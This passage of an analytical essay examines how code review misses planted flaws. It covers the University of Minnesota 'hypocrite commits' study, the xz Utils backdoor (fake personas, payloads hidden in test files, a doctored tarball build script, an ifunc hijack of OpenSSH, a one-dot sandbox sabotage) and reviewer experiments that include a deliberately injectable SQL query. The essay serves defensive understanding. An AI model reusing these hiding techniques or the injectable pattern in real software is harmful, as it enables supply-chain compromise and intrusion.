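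**Error paths** are branches that run only when something has gone wrong. Testing one in a driver can require both the hardware and a failure at the right moment, and drivers made up 62% of the kernel's code in 2020. Reviewers also expect error paths to release objects and print messages about them, and doing so in that order can cause a use-after-free.

Some functions release memory implicitly, with nothing in their names to indicate it. Wu and Lu counted 457 functions in the kernel that release memory, and more than half have no word such as "release" or "dealloc" in their names. Reference counting makes a release even harder to spot, because the same call to `put_device` is harmless when the count is two but releases the object when the count is one.

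An alias is another pointer to the same memory. If a patch frees memory through one pointer and the calling function later uses an alias, searching for the first pointer's name won't find that use. Static analyzers often miss it too.

The researchers also suspected indirect calls, whose target depends on what happens while the program runs.

### How often reviewers caught such flaws

Wu and Lu then estimated a catch rate, the share of flawed changes that reviewers stop before the project accepts them. They collected two groups of use-after-free flaws from January 2015 to August 2020, those that maintainers identified and blocked during review and those discovered after they had entered the kernel. The catch rate is the number of blocked flaws divided by the total in both groups.

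| What the flaw involves | Catch rate |
| --- | --- |
| Baseline for use-after-free flaws | 56.6% |
| Error path | 42.0% |
| Alias | 38.4% |
| Implicit release | 36.3% |
| Concurrency | 19.4% |
| Indirect call | 5 of 9 cases |

The formula leaves out flaws that nobody has found. Suppose reviewers blocked 100 flaws and people later found 77 that had slipped through. The catch rate would be about 56%, but if another 77 remain undiscovered in the kernel, the true rate is 39%. Wu and Lu therefore call their figures upper bounds. The error is probably largest for concurrency, because flaws that reviewers find hard to see are also hard for everyone else to find later.

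They do not discuss an error in the other direction, though. A reviewer can reject a flawed patch without noticing the flaw, perhaps because the patch is clumsy or solves a problem that doesn't exist. Such a patch never enters the kernel, but it does not count as caught, since nobody identified the use-after-free in it. So the table is a better estimate of how often reviewers recognize these flaws than of how often they keep them out of the kernel.

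The differences between the rows are also less clear than they look. Except for indirect calls, the paper gives percentages without case counts. The categories also overlap, since the MDIO flaw involves both an error path and an implicit release. The figure for indirect calls, 5 out of 9, is about the same as the baseline, so it is not evidence that indirect calls make review harder.

Wu and Lu also compared how long the flaws survived in the kernel. Concurrency was again the worst, with the longest survival, but error paths came second even though they have the highest catch rate of the four features. One plausible explanation is that reviewers can read an error path as easily as any other code, but users rarely run it, so a flaw that review misses may stay for years.

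All of these rates come from honest mistakes. A real attacker would put the flaw where it is hardest to check, and could try again after a rejection. Even if reviewers catch flawed patches at the baseline rate of 56.6%, someone who sends three has an 82% chance of getting at least one accepted, provided the reviews are independent. They may not be, because reviewers are likely to look more closely at a third patch from a new contributor whose first two were rejected. An honest contributor may also have years of good work behind them, which a new outsider lacks. The historical rates are good evidence of which facts reviewers overlook, but weaker evidence of an attacker's chances.

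### The live test

Wu and Lu reported that they sent three flawed patches, each under five lines, from a random Gmail account. They said that whenever a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they immediately pointed out the flaw, asked the maintainer not to apply the patch and supplied a correct one. They wrote that the maintainers confirmed in all three cases that they would not go ahead with the flawed patch. Wu and Lu (2020) repeated this in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* after the paper's abstract had drawn criticism.

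The public record does not match. It consists mainly of the emails themselves, the researchers' later patch-by-patch account in University of Minnesota's *A Full Disclosure of the Case Study of the “Hypocrite Commits” Paper* (2021), and an investigation by the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, a group of senior kernel developers. Lu's reply to the board, *Re: Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (Lu, 2021), quotes its report. There were five patches, sent under two false names:

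| Sent in 2020 | Name used | Apparent purpose | Flawed? | Outcome |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| August 4 | James Bond | Fix a reference-count leak | No, and not part of the study | Maintainers ignored it |
| August 9 | James Bond | Fix a memory leak in the text console | Yes | A reviewer remembered the same mistake from 2019 |
| August 20 | George Acosta | Add an error message to an encryption driver | No, though the researchers had meant it to be | The maintainer merged it |
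| August 20 | George Acosta | Fix a reference-count leak in a RapidIO driver | Yes | A reviewer objected to other faults |
| August 21 | James Bond | Lower a reference count in another driver | Yes | The maintainer objected to other faults |

Four of the patches belonged to the study. Three had a real flaw and never entered the kernel, while the fourth was harmless and did. According to the board, the researchers tried to make this fourth patch bad but failed because they did not understand how the kernel handles PCI drivers. They asked the maintainer about it after he had accepted it, and learned that it was fine. The paper nevertheless presents it as a working example, which the researchers later admitted they should have explained. University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) counts four study patches,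 one of them valid, but incorrectly says that all four "were stopped before making it past the review stage".

Why the three flawed patches failed matters more for judging code review than the fact that they did.

Bond (2020), in *[PATCH] tty/vt*, offered to fix a memory leak in the table that the console uses to match characters with shapes in a font. The message quoted a leak report from Syzkaller, an automatic testing tool. If the kernel could not get memory for the next piece of the table, the patch released an earlier piece, but the rest of the table still pointed to it. Jiri Slaby, a maintainer, rejected the patch seven hours later because it reminded him of a change that maintainers had accepted and then removed in 2019. Hutchings, in *Revert "consolemap: Fix a memory leaking bug"* (2019), had explained at the time that there had been no leak, and that the "fix" introduced both a real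 leak and a use-after-free. Slaby's objection therefore covered the planted flaw, but he raised it because he remembered the earlier change. That change was nearly the same, and it had passed review in 2019, when reviewers had no such precedent to remember.

Acosta (2020), in *[PATCH] rapidio* added a single `put_device` line to an error path in the RapidIO driver. The next line printed an error message that used the same device, which the kernel might just have released. The reviewer, Dan Carpenter, replied four and a half hours later. He pointed out a different use-after-free, already in the driver, in which the function left a list entry pointing to released memory after a failure. He also found the error handling messy and recommended moving the `put_device` calls to a shared block at the end of the function. That would have fixed the planted flaw by putting the release after the error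 message, where Wu and Lu say a correct fix belongs, but nothing in his reply suggests that he had seen the flaw.

The August 21 patch would have lowered a count that a cleanup function already lowers. According to the researchers, the driver's maintainer missed this and objected to a different problem in the code. The submitter then replied that the patch was wrong and apologized for the bother.

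The kernel's review kept out all three flawed patches, and the board concluded that it "worked as intended". But reviewers identified the planted flaw in only one of the three, helped by a lucky precedent. Three cases are also too few to establish much, since reviewers who stopped only 56.6% of such patches would still stop three in a row 18% of the time.

The record also doesn't support Wu and Lu's claim to have shown that the attack is practical. They were supposed to warn the maintainer once a reviewer approved a flawed patch, but the record shows no reviewer approving any of the three, so it seems they never reached that point. Their best evidence was the 2019 console patch, which came from somebody else and was unknown to them when they sent theirs. They also claim in the FAQ that their patches ultimately helped to fix three real bugs. But the console leak was a false alarm, and the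 board found that the submitter ignored Carpenter's suggestions and sent nothing further for that driver.

### The ban and the re-review

The dispute began in November 2020, when Lu posted the paper's abstract on Twitter, and grew much larger the following spring. On April 6, 2021, the university's researchers resumed sending kernel patches after a seven-month break, and the new ones were poor. On April 20, Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable releases, accused them of experimenting on maintainers again and told other developers to reject everything from the university. In *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers*, an article for the Linux news site LWN, Edge (2021) followed Kroah-Hartman in reporting that one of the April patches was not an honest mistake.

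That suspicion was wrong. The researchers explained in University of Minnesota's *An open letter to the Linux community* (2021) that the April patches came from a new project to find bugs automatically. The board's report treats the resumed attack as a "perception". Cook (2021), a board member, conceded that a notice's wording was "sub-optimal" after another developer complained that it had attributed "bad faith" to the university's patches in general. The mistake is easy to understand, because the maintainers had learned that the group sent bad patches on purpose and could not tell an author's intention from a bad patch.

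They therefore rechecked the group's earlier work, 435 commits in all. The board sorted them as follows:

| Finding | Commits |
| --- | --- |
| Correct | 349 |
| Incorrect and still in need of a fix | 39 |
| Incorrect, but already fixed or removed | 25 |
| No longer relevant, because the code was gone | 12 |
| Older than the research group | 9 |
| Incorrect, and removed at the author's request | 1 |

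No sign of further planted flaws emerged. But about one commit in seven was wrong, although each had passed ordinary review, and most of the wrong ones were still in the kernel until people went back to look. (The 39 apparently include the harmless study patch, which Kroah-Hartman wanted out because of its false name.) This result is a second, independent indication that kernel review lets through many small mistakes in patches presented as fixes. It doesn't give a catch rate, since nobody counted how many of the group's bad patches reviewers had rejected over the years, and an incorrect fix is often no security risk. Recovery also took many people's work, and the report thanks 85 developers for their help.

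### The ethics dispute

Wu and Lu defended the test by arguing that they were studying a process, not people. They collected no personal data, kept the patches tiny to save reviewers' time, and said that users have a right to know about the risk. Their university's ethics board agreed that the test was not research on human subjects, but they asked the board only after critics of the abstract told them to. They also acknowledged wasting maintainers' time.

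Critics objected to the deception and the lack of consent. The Technical Advisory Board found the RapidIO patch especially hurtful because the reviewer was trying to teach someone he took for a beginner. The false names also broke the kernel's rules, which require every contributor to sign a legal statement about where the code came from.

Readers debated the test in the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021). One compared it to the fake phishing emails that companies send their own staff, and thought it absurd to invoke codes written for medical experiments. Another replied that someone senior at the company approves those emails and that the staff have usually accepted such monitoring as a condition of their job. One of the four researchers who had complained to the conference added that wasted time counts as harm, and that a study that relies on deception needs close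 oversight by an independent committee. This position seems stronger because it still allows such a test. The Minnesota researchers could have asked the kernel's leaders for permission without warning the individual reviewers, much as a company does with its phishing emails.

On April 26, 2021, Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew the paper from the IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy, which had accepted it, so it never appeared in the proceedings. They said they did so because they had studied the kernel community without appropriate consent and approval. Cook accepted the university's apology on May 9 and thanked the group for its earlier bug fixes. The withdrawal was about ethics and does not by itself discredit the historical data, but the errors in the paper's account of the live test are a reason to treat its other figures with some care.

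### Would the proposed remedies work?

Wu and Lu suggested that projects make contributors promise not to introduce bugs on purpose. But an attacker would make the promise anyway, just as the researchers had signed the kernel's existing statement with invented names.

They also proposed verifying who contributors are, but admitted that this is difficult online, partly because Git, which the kernel and most other projects use to record changes, lets people enter any name and email address as a commit's author. GitHub then links the commit to whichever account has registered that address. In *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult*, an NDSS security conference paper, Holtgrave and colleagues (2025) showed how an attacker can use this to make a commit appear to come from a trusted developer. An attacker can also register an unclaimed address that appears in old commits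 and so take credit for someone else's good work. The study found that 86% of about 50,000 important GitHub projects were open to this kind of abuse, and that more than half a million addresses could be claimed. Digital signatures would prevent much of it, as Theodore Ts'o had argued after the 2003 attempt on the kernel, but 95% of the users in the study had never signed a commit.

Better authentication would stop people from impersonating trusted contributors, but it would not have stopped Wu and Lu. Their own names were an asset, since their group had contributed roughly 400 bug fixes to the kernel in two years. Reviewers also made poor use of the names they saw. "James Bond" struck Kroah-Hartman as odd ("Nice name..."), and the maintainers later ignored the August 4 patch, the only one in the series sent in good faith, because they knew the name was false. "George Acosta" was also a false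 name, but it sounded ordinary, and a patch sent under it got into the kernel.

Kroah-Hartman rejected the idea of treating some contributors as suspects. In an exchange reprinted in the researchers' disclosure, Wu asked him generally about malicious contributors, without mentioning the patches then under review. Kroah-Hartman answered that everyone makes mistakes, so reviewers have to check everyone's patches. He added that he does not re-review patches from the maintainers he accepts work from, because he trusts them to have reviewed the patches and to fix any that turn out to be wrong. This is a sensible way to handle honest errors, but it leaves the project dependent on the first reviewer's judgment and good faith to stop planted flaws.

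Better tools would address the cause more directly. Wu and Lu recommended analyzers that can follow aliases and concurrent code, and tests that deliberately make operations fail so that error paths run. Both would supply facts that a diff leaves out, but they would also produce more false alarms, such as warnings about failures that could never happen in practice. The console patch shows that false alarms can help an attacker. Its justification was a mistaken leak report from a respected tool, and Wu and Lu expected maintainers to trust the patch because of that report.

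Another proposal was to accept preventive patches, which remove an immature vulnerability before anyone completes it. For example, a programmer can clear a pointer after freeing its memory, so that a later use crashes instead of reading whatever is there now. The researchers believed that the kernel refuses such patches, but the rule they cite, that a patch must fix a real bug, applies to the stable releases. Kroah-Hartman told Wu that they were wrong and pointed to protections the kernel had added over the years to limit the damage from bugs. Scale is the bigger obstacle. Wu and Lu's tool found more than 30,000 pointers that the code had neither cleared nor reused after freeing their memory, and clearing one pointer does not clear its aliases, such as the caller's own pointer to `bus` in the MDIO case.

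Wu and Lu also wanted more people to see each patch, since usually only a few key maintainers respond. The console patch supports this to a point. It failed because one person happened to remember the earlier change, but a project can't count on that person reading every message. In the same email thread, Kroah-Hartman proposed a source code comment to the effect of "this is fine, don't touch it!", so that the next reviewer would find the missing fact next to the relevant line. Slaby preferred to correct the tool that kept reporting the leak.

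## The xz Utils backdoor

The Minnesota researchers sent their patches as strangers, so each patch needed a maintainer's approval. The attacker behind the xz Utils backdoor spent just over a year becoming a maintainer and about another year working as one before planting it. xz Utils is a set of free tools for compressing files, and most Linux systems have its library, liblzma, installed. Two releases in early 2024 contained a backdoor that let the holder of a secret key run any command on certain Linux servers without logging in. Most of the backdoor was not source code, so reviewers had little code to read.

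### How "Jia Tan" became a maintainer

Lasse Collin, who led the design of the .xz file format in the 2000s, maintained xz Utils as an unpaid hobby. On October 29, 2021, someone using the name Jia Tan sent the project's mailing list a patch that added a settings file for text editors. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Cox, 2024) calls the patch innocuous. More harmless patches followed, and Collin first added one of Tan's changes to the project in February 2022.

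That April, "Jigar Kumar" began complaining on the list that Collin had not yet accepted one of Tan's patches. In May, "Dennis Ens" asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version of xz. Collin apologized for being slow and mentioned that Tan might get a bigger role. In June, both Kumar and Ens called for a new maintainer. When Kumar wrote that Collin had lost interest, Collin replied that he had not, but that long-term mental health problems limited what he could do. Ens expressed sympathy and asked why Collin didn't hand one of the two versions to someone else. On June 29, Collin told the list that Tan was "practically a co-maintainer already".

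Kumar and Ens were probably fake identities. Cox cites the journalist Brian Krebs, who noted that many of these email addresses appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data. The evidence is circumstantial, though, and *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) found no direct link between Tan and the other accounts.

By the end of December 2022, Tan could change the repository without going through Collin. Over the next year or so, Tan also took over the release archives, the bug reports from Google's fuzzing service and the project's website. Przymus and Durieux classified every line Tan changed and found more documentation and translation than program code, which is work that builds a reputation without attracting much scrutiny. They counted eight malicious commits in 2.6 years of activity. Collin later reviewed Tan's commits one by one and published his notes on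 the project's site, Tukaani. He marked most of them "OK" and found some ordinary slips, such as a memory leak in a test, so anyone who judged Tan on this record would have had good reason for trust.

### From a test file to the login server

The target was OpenSSH, the program that administrators use to log in to remote servers. OpenSSH doesn't use liblzma, but Debian, Fedora and some other Linux distributions had modified its server to report to systemd, the program that starts and supervises services. The modified server used systemd's library, which in turn used liblzma, so it loaded Collin's compression code whenever it started.

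Cox (2024), in *The xz attack shell script*, and Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, explain how the attacker used this connection:

1. A distribution builds its xz package from the official release archive. An altered build file in the archive finds one of the project's test files and runs a script hidden inside it.
2. The script checks whether the machine is suitable. If it is, the script takes a ready-compiled piece of code out of another test file and adds it to liblzma.
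3. When the login server starts, it loads liblzma, and the added code runs before the server's own.
4. The added code replaces a function that the server uses to check digital signatures during a login. The replacement runs the attacker's command if the request carries the right key. Otherwise it apparently lets the normal check go ahead, so ordinary users can still log in.

The third step depends on timing. A running program keeps a table of addresses for the functions it borrows from libraries. Many programs fill in this table at start-up and then lock it, so that a later memory bug can't redirect a call. Some library functions, called indirect functions or ifuncs, come in several versions for different processors, and a small selector routine picks the best one at start-up. In the login server, the selectors run before the table is locked, so the backdoor could edit the table by taking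 over two selectors in liblzma.

xz had used ifuncs only since June 2023, when "Hans Jansen" contributed them as a speed improvement. Collin reworked part of that contribution himself. Jansen then disappeared until March 2024, when the account asked Debian to adopt a backdoored release. Even so, Przymus and Durieux leave open whether the original patch belonged to the attack. It did what it promised, and many libraries use ifuncs for the same purpose.

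### What reviewers of the repository could see

Tan committed the test files on February 23, 2024. A compression library needs odd and damaged files to test that it handles them properly, and xz had a folder for them long before Tan arrived. According to its README, people had made many of the files by hand, so there was no better "source code" than the files themselves. A diff of such a file shows only that some binary data has changed. A reviewer who opened "bad-3-corrupt" would have found garbage, as expected of a test file with that name.

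Collin's review indicates that the tests in version 5.6.0 used the new files, because the project's test script automatically tries every file in the folder. Freund had written that no test used them, which would have been a clue. A better clue was that the files came without the program that had generated them. A reviewer can read a generator and run it to see whether it produces the same file. Collin has since kept a small related change in the repository in case someone adds "proper files along with a generator program".

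The altered build file escaped review because it was never in the repository. Like many C projects, xz publishes each release as an archive, or tarball, with extra files generated from the repository so that people can build the program without installing the tools that generate them. Differences between the archive and the repository are therefore normal. Tan's archive included a doctored copy of `build-to-host.m4`, a standard file of this kind. Cox thinks the changes would have looked fairly plausible even to someone who compared the copy with the original. They raise the version number, update the copyright year and add a few inscrutable lines to an already hard-to-read file. Tan had also added the file's name to the repository's ignore list. Collin considers that entry correct in itself, since the normal tools create the file too.

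Collin had once made the kind of comparison that could have exposed the attack. Before version 5.4.5 was released, he noticed that Tan's archives had the wrong ownership and permission data. Tan had probably used the wrong command but didn't admit it, and Collin kept asking questions. He built his own archive, compared its contents with Tan's, found nothing else wrong and let the release go ahead. His later review cleared every archive Tan made before 5.6.0, including those for 5.4.5. The same comparison for 5.6.0 would have turned up the doctored file, although Collin would still have had to recognize that it was more than a newer version of the standard one.

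### What analyzers and fuzzers could see

A static analyzer run on all the C code in the repository would have found no backdoor, because the C code didn't contain one. The attacker had compiled the malicious code in advance, then compressed and scrambled it inside the test files. The commands that started unpacking it were in the release archive, written in build languages that C analyzers do not process. In *Re: Update on the distro-backdoor-scanner effort*, a message to a security mailing list, Jacob Bachmeyer (2024) judged that the attacker had hidden the reusable parts where "no scanner could plausibly find" them.

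The backdoor was easier to detect once a distribution had built the package, because the compiled liblzma contained selector routines that did far more than select a function. Within 24 hours of the disclosure, the security company Binarly released a free tool that recognizes these routines without running the library. Binarly's *Persistent Risk* (2025) claims that the tool raises almost no false alarms. Static analysis could therefore catch the backdoor if it examined the compiled library instead of the source. But Binarly's researchers knew which trick to look for, unlike anyone who checked xz in February 2024.

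Fuzzing also missed the backdoor, and one of Tan's changes may have been meant to ensure this. Google's OSS-Fuzz service regularly fuzzes important open-source projects, including xz. On July 7, 2023, Tan turned off ifuncs in the service's configuration for xz, saying they are incompatible with AddressSanitizer, the memory checker. The hidden script stops if ifuncs are off, so the change also kept the backdoor out of the fuzzing builds. Bachmeyer suspects this was the purpose, but Cox thinks the change may well have been innocent. Ifuncs do have a history of trouble with such checkers, so the people who run OSS-Fuzz had no strong reason to reject the change.

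The change probably made no difference. The script added the backdoor only when gcc was used to build a Debian or Red Hat package, whereas OSS-Fuzz doesn't build packages and normally uses Clang. Even if OSS-Fuzz had tested a backdoored copy of the library, it would probably have found nothing wrong. A contributor to an Openwall mailing list (2024) pointed out that the backdoor did not appear to affect xz or liblzma and used the library only as a way into the login server. A fuzzer feeds liblzma strange compressed files and waits for a crash. To detect the backdoor, it would have had to send the login server requests that carried the attacker's key.

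### One stray dot

Tan also made a change in readable source code that would have suited an underhanded-code contest. It affected xz's use of Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program give up rights it doesn't need, such as access to most files. The aim, according to the Linux kernel documentation's *Landlock* (2026), is to limit the harm from bugs and from unexpected or malicious behavior. The xz command uses Landlock where it can. To check for support, the build process tries to compile a tiny C program that uses the feature. If that fails, the build process treats Landlock as unavailable and continues without it.

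In late February 2024 Tan changed this tiny program. Collin (2024), in *CMake*, repaired it on March 30, the day after the backdoor became public:

```
 #include <sys/prctl.h>
-.
+
 void my_sandbox(void)
```

The minus sign marks the line Collin removed, which contains only a dot. A dot there is a syntax error in C, so the program never compiled and the build left out the sandbox on every system.

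The dot is visible, unlike the control characters in Trojan Source, but it's easy to overlook on an otherwise blank line. The project's records list Collin as the committer. Cox considered the possibility that Tan had forged the name, but thought it more likely that Collin, who knew the project best, had missed the dot. Collin's review supports this, since he found no sign of forged names.

The program never compiled, but the build process discarded the error message because such programs are expected to fail on older systems. Analyzers would be unlikely to help, because the C program is text inside a build script. Ordinary tests would still pass, since xz compresses files equally well without a sandbox. The project could have caught the mistake by building xz on a machine known to support Landlock and treating a failed check as an error. Przymus and Durieux report that the developers of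 CMake, the build tool involved, considered making such test programs harder to sabotage, and that the developers of Autoconf, a rival tool, were adding a syntax check.

Nobody knows what the dot was for. Landlock protects the xz command and not liblzma, so disabling it did not help the attack on login servers. The dot also affected only builds that use CMake, while the backdoor relied on xz's other build system. Cox's timeline places the dot in that other system's script, but Collin's repair shows it was in the CMake script. Cox suspects the dot was preparation for something else. An accident can't be ruled out, but Collin described the check as "sabotaged" in his patch. He has since read Tan's changes to blank lines carefully, and noted of one from November 2023, "It really is just space change, no dots."

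### The libarchive change

In 2021, the same account had also changed libarchive, a library that reads and writes archive files (Boehs, 2024, *Everything I know about the XZ backdoor*). The patch improved an error message but also replaced a function that filters out control characters with one that prints text unfiltered. A file name inside a malicious archive could then send commands to the user's terminal, which can do real harm in some terminal programs. The libarchive developers restored the filter after Freund's disclosure, and Maste (2024, *tar*) added their fix to the FreeBSD operating system on March 31.

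The evidence that this was an attack is thin. Fernandez (2024), in *escaping terminal control characters*, quotes two security specialists. Tavis Ormandy thought the change minor but "a bit suspicious" in hindsight. The other, who posts as Solar Designer, agreed that it was minor and guessed that it was an early test of whether the project would accept a patch that weakened security. He added that most command-line tools don't filter file names. GitHub's *unescaped pathnames may be printed in error cases* mentions several other places where libarchive prints error messages unfiltered, none connected with Tan's patch. An honest programmer could easily have made the same change. The patch stayed in libarchive for more than two years, until people had another reason to distrust Tan.

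### A half-second delay

Cox's timeline gives these dates for the last five weeks of the attack:

| Date in 2024 | Event |
| --- | --- |
| February 24 | Tan publishes version 5.6.0 |
| February 26 | Debian adds it to "unstable", its development branch |
| March 4 | Users of Red Hat's distributions start to see Valgrind errors in liblzma |
| March 5 | Version 5.6.0 reaches Debian's "testing" branch |
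| March 8 and 9 | Tan commits a sham fix, replaces the test files and publishes version 5.6.1 |
| March 27 | Debian adopts version 5.6.1 |
| March 28 | Tan asks Ubuntu to do the same. Andres Freund warns Debian and other distributors privately, and Debian returns to an older version |
| March 29 | Freund publishes the discovery |

Valgrind is a tool that monitors how a program uses memory as it runs. The errors on March 4 came from the backdoor, so a routine check had detected it more than three weeks before anyone understood what it was. The reports went to the project, where Tan answered them. Tan had a believable excuse because the new ifuncs had a real bug, which had already caused crashes on Gentoo, another distribution. On March 8 Tan committed a change that was supposed to fix the Valgrind errors but did not. The next day Tan fixed the fault in the backdoor itself by replacing the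 two test files. Tan wrote in the commit message that the old files had used random data from Tan's own computer and that the new ones would be easier to reproduce.

Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, had seen Valgrind errors too. He also noticed that SSH logins on his Debian unstable systems used a lot of processor time. When he measured a login attempt with a nonexistent username, the server took 0.8 seconds to refuse it, up from 0.3 seconds. The backdoor caused the delay by searching the names of functions in memory for the ones it needed. The login server starts a fresh copy of itself for each connection, so every attempt repeated the search.

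To hinder investigation, the backdoor's author designed it to stay inactive if someone started the server by hand from an ordinary terminal, or if certain debugging tools were running. Freund therefore saw no delay at first when he started the server himself. He worked out which settings mattered, recorded the processor's path through the code with the backdoor active and inactive, and compared the two recordings to find where they diverged, which led him to liblzma. He first assumed that somebody had tampered with Debian's package, then found the same code in the official release. He also considered that Tan might be the victim of a break-in, but thought this less likely because Tan had discussed the supposed fixes on several mailing lists.

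By then the test files had been public for five weeks and packagers at several distributions had handled the archives, but nobody had reported the backdoor from reading either. Its behavior exposed it only because its author's mistakes had caused memory errors and a slow search, without which Freund would have had no reason to look.

The backdoored versions reached Debian's testing and unstable branches, Fedora Rawhide and the Fedora 40 beta. Binarly also lists openSUSE, and Linux Compatible collected notices from Arch Linux and Kali Linux, though Arch's login server doesn't load liblzma. Most of these were development versions or continuously updated distributions. As far as Przymus and Durieux know, nobody used the backdoor against a real system.

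An unrelated clean-up might have stopped the attack anyway. On February 29 a developer proposed that systemd's library stop loading liblzma automatically, and the systemd project accepted the change on March 5. Some people have suggested that Tan rushed because of it. Version 5.6.0 came out five days before the proposal, although systemd developers had mentioned the idea in late January. The change would have protected distributions only once they adopted the new systemd.

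### What changed afterwards

Arch Linux began building xz from the repository instead of the release archive on March 28, and Haiku switched to repository snapshots two days later. Building from the repository would have defeated the backdoor, because the altered build file that triggered it existed only in the archive. Tukaani's *xz backdoor* (2024) explains that Collin left the malicious test files in the repository's history because they are harmless without that build file. An attacker with Tan's access could have committed the altered file to the repository too, but the change would then have appeared in a diff with a name and date.

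Reproducible builds also gained attention. A build is reproducible if anyone who compiles the same source under the same conditions gets a byte-for-byte identical file. Comparing such builds exposes tampering on the computer that does the compiling, but in xz the tampering was in what people took to be the source. Two people who each built a Debian package from Tan's archive could have got identical libraries, both with the backdoor. To detect the tampering, they would have had to compare a build from the archive with one from the repository, or regenerate the archive and check that it matched the original.

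Collin did the latter when he checked Tan's earlier archives. The translation files he regenerated were identical to the published ones. The PDF manuals differed because they contain their creation time and vary with the version of the software that made them, so he could only confirm that they looked normal and were about the right size. An attacker could hide something in any generated file of this kind, and Collin has since dropped the ready-made programming documentation from the archives, partly to reduce the number of such files.

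Other developers removed dependencies. OpenSSH added a short piece of its own code for reporting to systemd, so distributions no longer need to link the login server to systemd's library. Przymus and Durieux list similar efforts in other projects. Removing dependencies reduces the number of programs a malicious library can reach, though it doesn't make the library easier to detect.

Volunteers also searched whole distributions for similar attacks. In April 2024, in an exchange quoted in Bachmeyer's message, Hank Leininger reported that every match outside xz was a false alarm. His group was also trying to trace the origin of every build file of the type Tan had altered. They had tools to compare each file with known good copies, but had only spot-checked the differences that needed human review. Bachmeyer doubted that searching for text from the xz attack would uncover another attack, since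 a different attacker would hide the trigger differently. He suggested looking for build commands with the same name but different definitions. More recently, researchers have built Lily, a tool for vetting new releases.

Collin published clean versions on May 29, 2024, with the first complete edition of his review, which covers Tan's commits since December 2022. He had removed ifunc support. The project has a second maintainer again, a longtime contributor to Gentoo and xz.

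### Backdoored copies in 2025

On August 12, 2025, more than sixteen months after Freund's disclosure, Binarly reported that copies of the backdoor were still available on Docker Hub, a public registry of images. An image is a ready-made package of software used to start an isolated environment called a container. Twelve of Debian's own images contained a backdoored liblzma. Images that other people had built on top of these also contained it, bringing the total to more than 35. A few of the affected images were the latest versions available.

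Debian's maintainers declined to remove their images. The Hacker News (2025) quotes them as saying they had deliberately left the images up "as a historical curiosity" and that the conditions for an attack were extremely unlikely in a container. The risk is small because a container would have to run an SSH server, which most don't, and the attacker would need both network access to it and the secret key. Binarly accepts much of this but objects to leaving the images where anyone can download them and build on them. Debian could have kept its historical record without offering the images for ordinary use.

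Binarly's count is a minimum. Docker Hub has nearly 12 million repositories, far too many to scan, and offers no way to look up which images build on a given one, so the researchers checked a list of likely candidates compiled by hand. They looked only at Debian-based images, because Debian keeps its old images online, and they did not trace derived images beyond the first generation.

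## Experiments on what code reviewers notice

Only a few people looked at each change in the Minnesota and xz cases, so neither shows how often a typical reviewer would miss a given flaw. Measuring that requires showing the same flawed change to many reviewers, which Larissa Braz of the University of Zurich and colleagues did in two online experiments, mostly with professional programmers. Many participants missed flaws that nobody had tried to hide, but they did much better when told to look for security problems.

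### Two missing checks

The first experiment, in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (Braz, Fregnan and colleagues, 2021), tested whether reviewers notice when code fails to check the data it receives. The researchers recruited 146 volunteers through online forums, social media and professional contacts. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional experience, and almost two-thirds reviewed code every day. Each reviewed a Java change of about 140 lines for managing employees' vacations, shown as a diff in a copy of a common review tool. The researchers told them only that the study aimed to improve code review and did not mention security.

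Each volunteer saw one of two versions, chosen at random. In the first, the program pastes an employee's ID into a database command:

```
String query =
    "SELECT * FROM tblemployees WHERE employeeID='" + employeeID + "'";
```

This flaw, known as SQL injection, is the same one as in the earlier example of a website that looks up its users. In the second version, the program accepts a whole number without checking its range, and a negative number works to the user's advantage. (A request for minus five days off might add five days to the balance, for example.)

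The same kind of check would fix either flaw. But the SQL injection attack is well known; textbooks explain it and a popular web comic jokes about it. Reviewers can see the danger in the unchecked number only if they think of an attack themselves.

| | SQL injection | Unchecked number |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Reviewers | 80 | 66 |
| Found it in the first review | 52 (65%) | 14 (21%) |
| Found it only after a warning | 13 (16%) | 7 (11%) |
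| Never found it | 15 (19%) | 45 (68%) |

Reviewers were about three times as likely to find the SQL injection as the unchecked number. Braz and colleagues write that reviewers were seven times more likely to find it, but this figure is a ratio of odds. The odds were 52 to 28 for the SQL injection and 14 to 52 for the unchecked number, a ratio of 6.9.

After the first review, the researchers told everyone that the change contained a vulnerability, but not what kind, and let those who had missed it look again. Nearly half of the people who had missed the SQL injection now found it, and most of them said they had needed a reminder to think about security. Only 7 of the 52 who had missed the unchecked number found it. A warning seems to help people who would recognize a flaw but are not looking for one, and to do less for people who would have to work out the attack.

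The researchers had also put an ordinary bug in the change to check that the volunteers were making an effort. About half found it, and they were no more or less likely than the others to find the vulnerability. In eight comments, people who missed the unchecked number explained that they had mistaken this bug for the vulnerability.

The experiment compares two different flaws, so it doesn't isolate the effect of a visible attack. Reviewers may recognize SQL injection because they have seen it often, without thinking through any attack. Either way, an attacker has good reason to avoid flaws that reviewers recognize easily.

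### Telling reviewers to look for security flaws

*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested whether an instruction at the start of the review would help reviewers notice vulnerabilities. The 150 volunteers reviewed a 160-line Java change that registers users on a website and had two flaws. If a database command failed, the program wrote the whole command to a log, including the user's email address and unencrypted password. The program also scrambled passwords with MD5, an algorithm that specialists have long considered broken and that is so fast that an attacker can try huge numbers of guesses.

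The researchers assigned the volunteers to four groups at random. They said nothing about security to the first group. They told the second group that they were interested in security issues and explained what a vulnerability is. The third and fourth groups got the same instruction and a checklist each. One checklist had 22 questions, adapted from a 78-item list by OWASP, a nonprofit that promotes software security. The other had seven, all relevant to this change. Both included questions that pointed to the two flaws.

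| Group | Reviewers | Found the password in the log | Found MD5 |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| No mention of security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Security instruction | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| Instruction and general checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| Instruction and tailored checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

(The paper prints the last figure as 61%, but 28 of 41 is 68%.)

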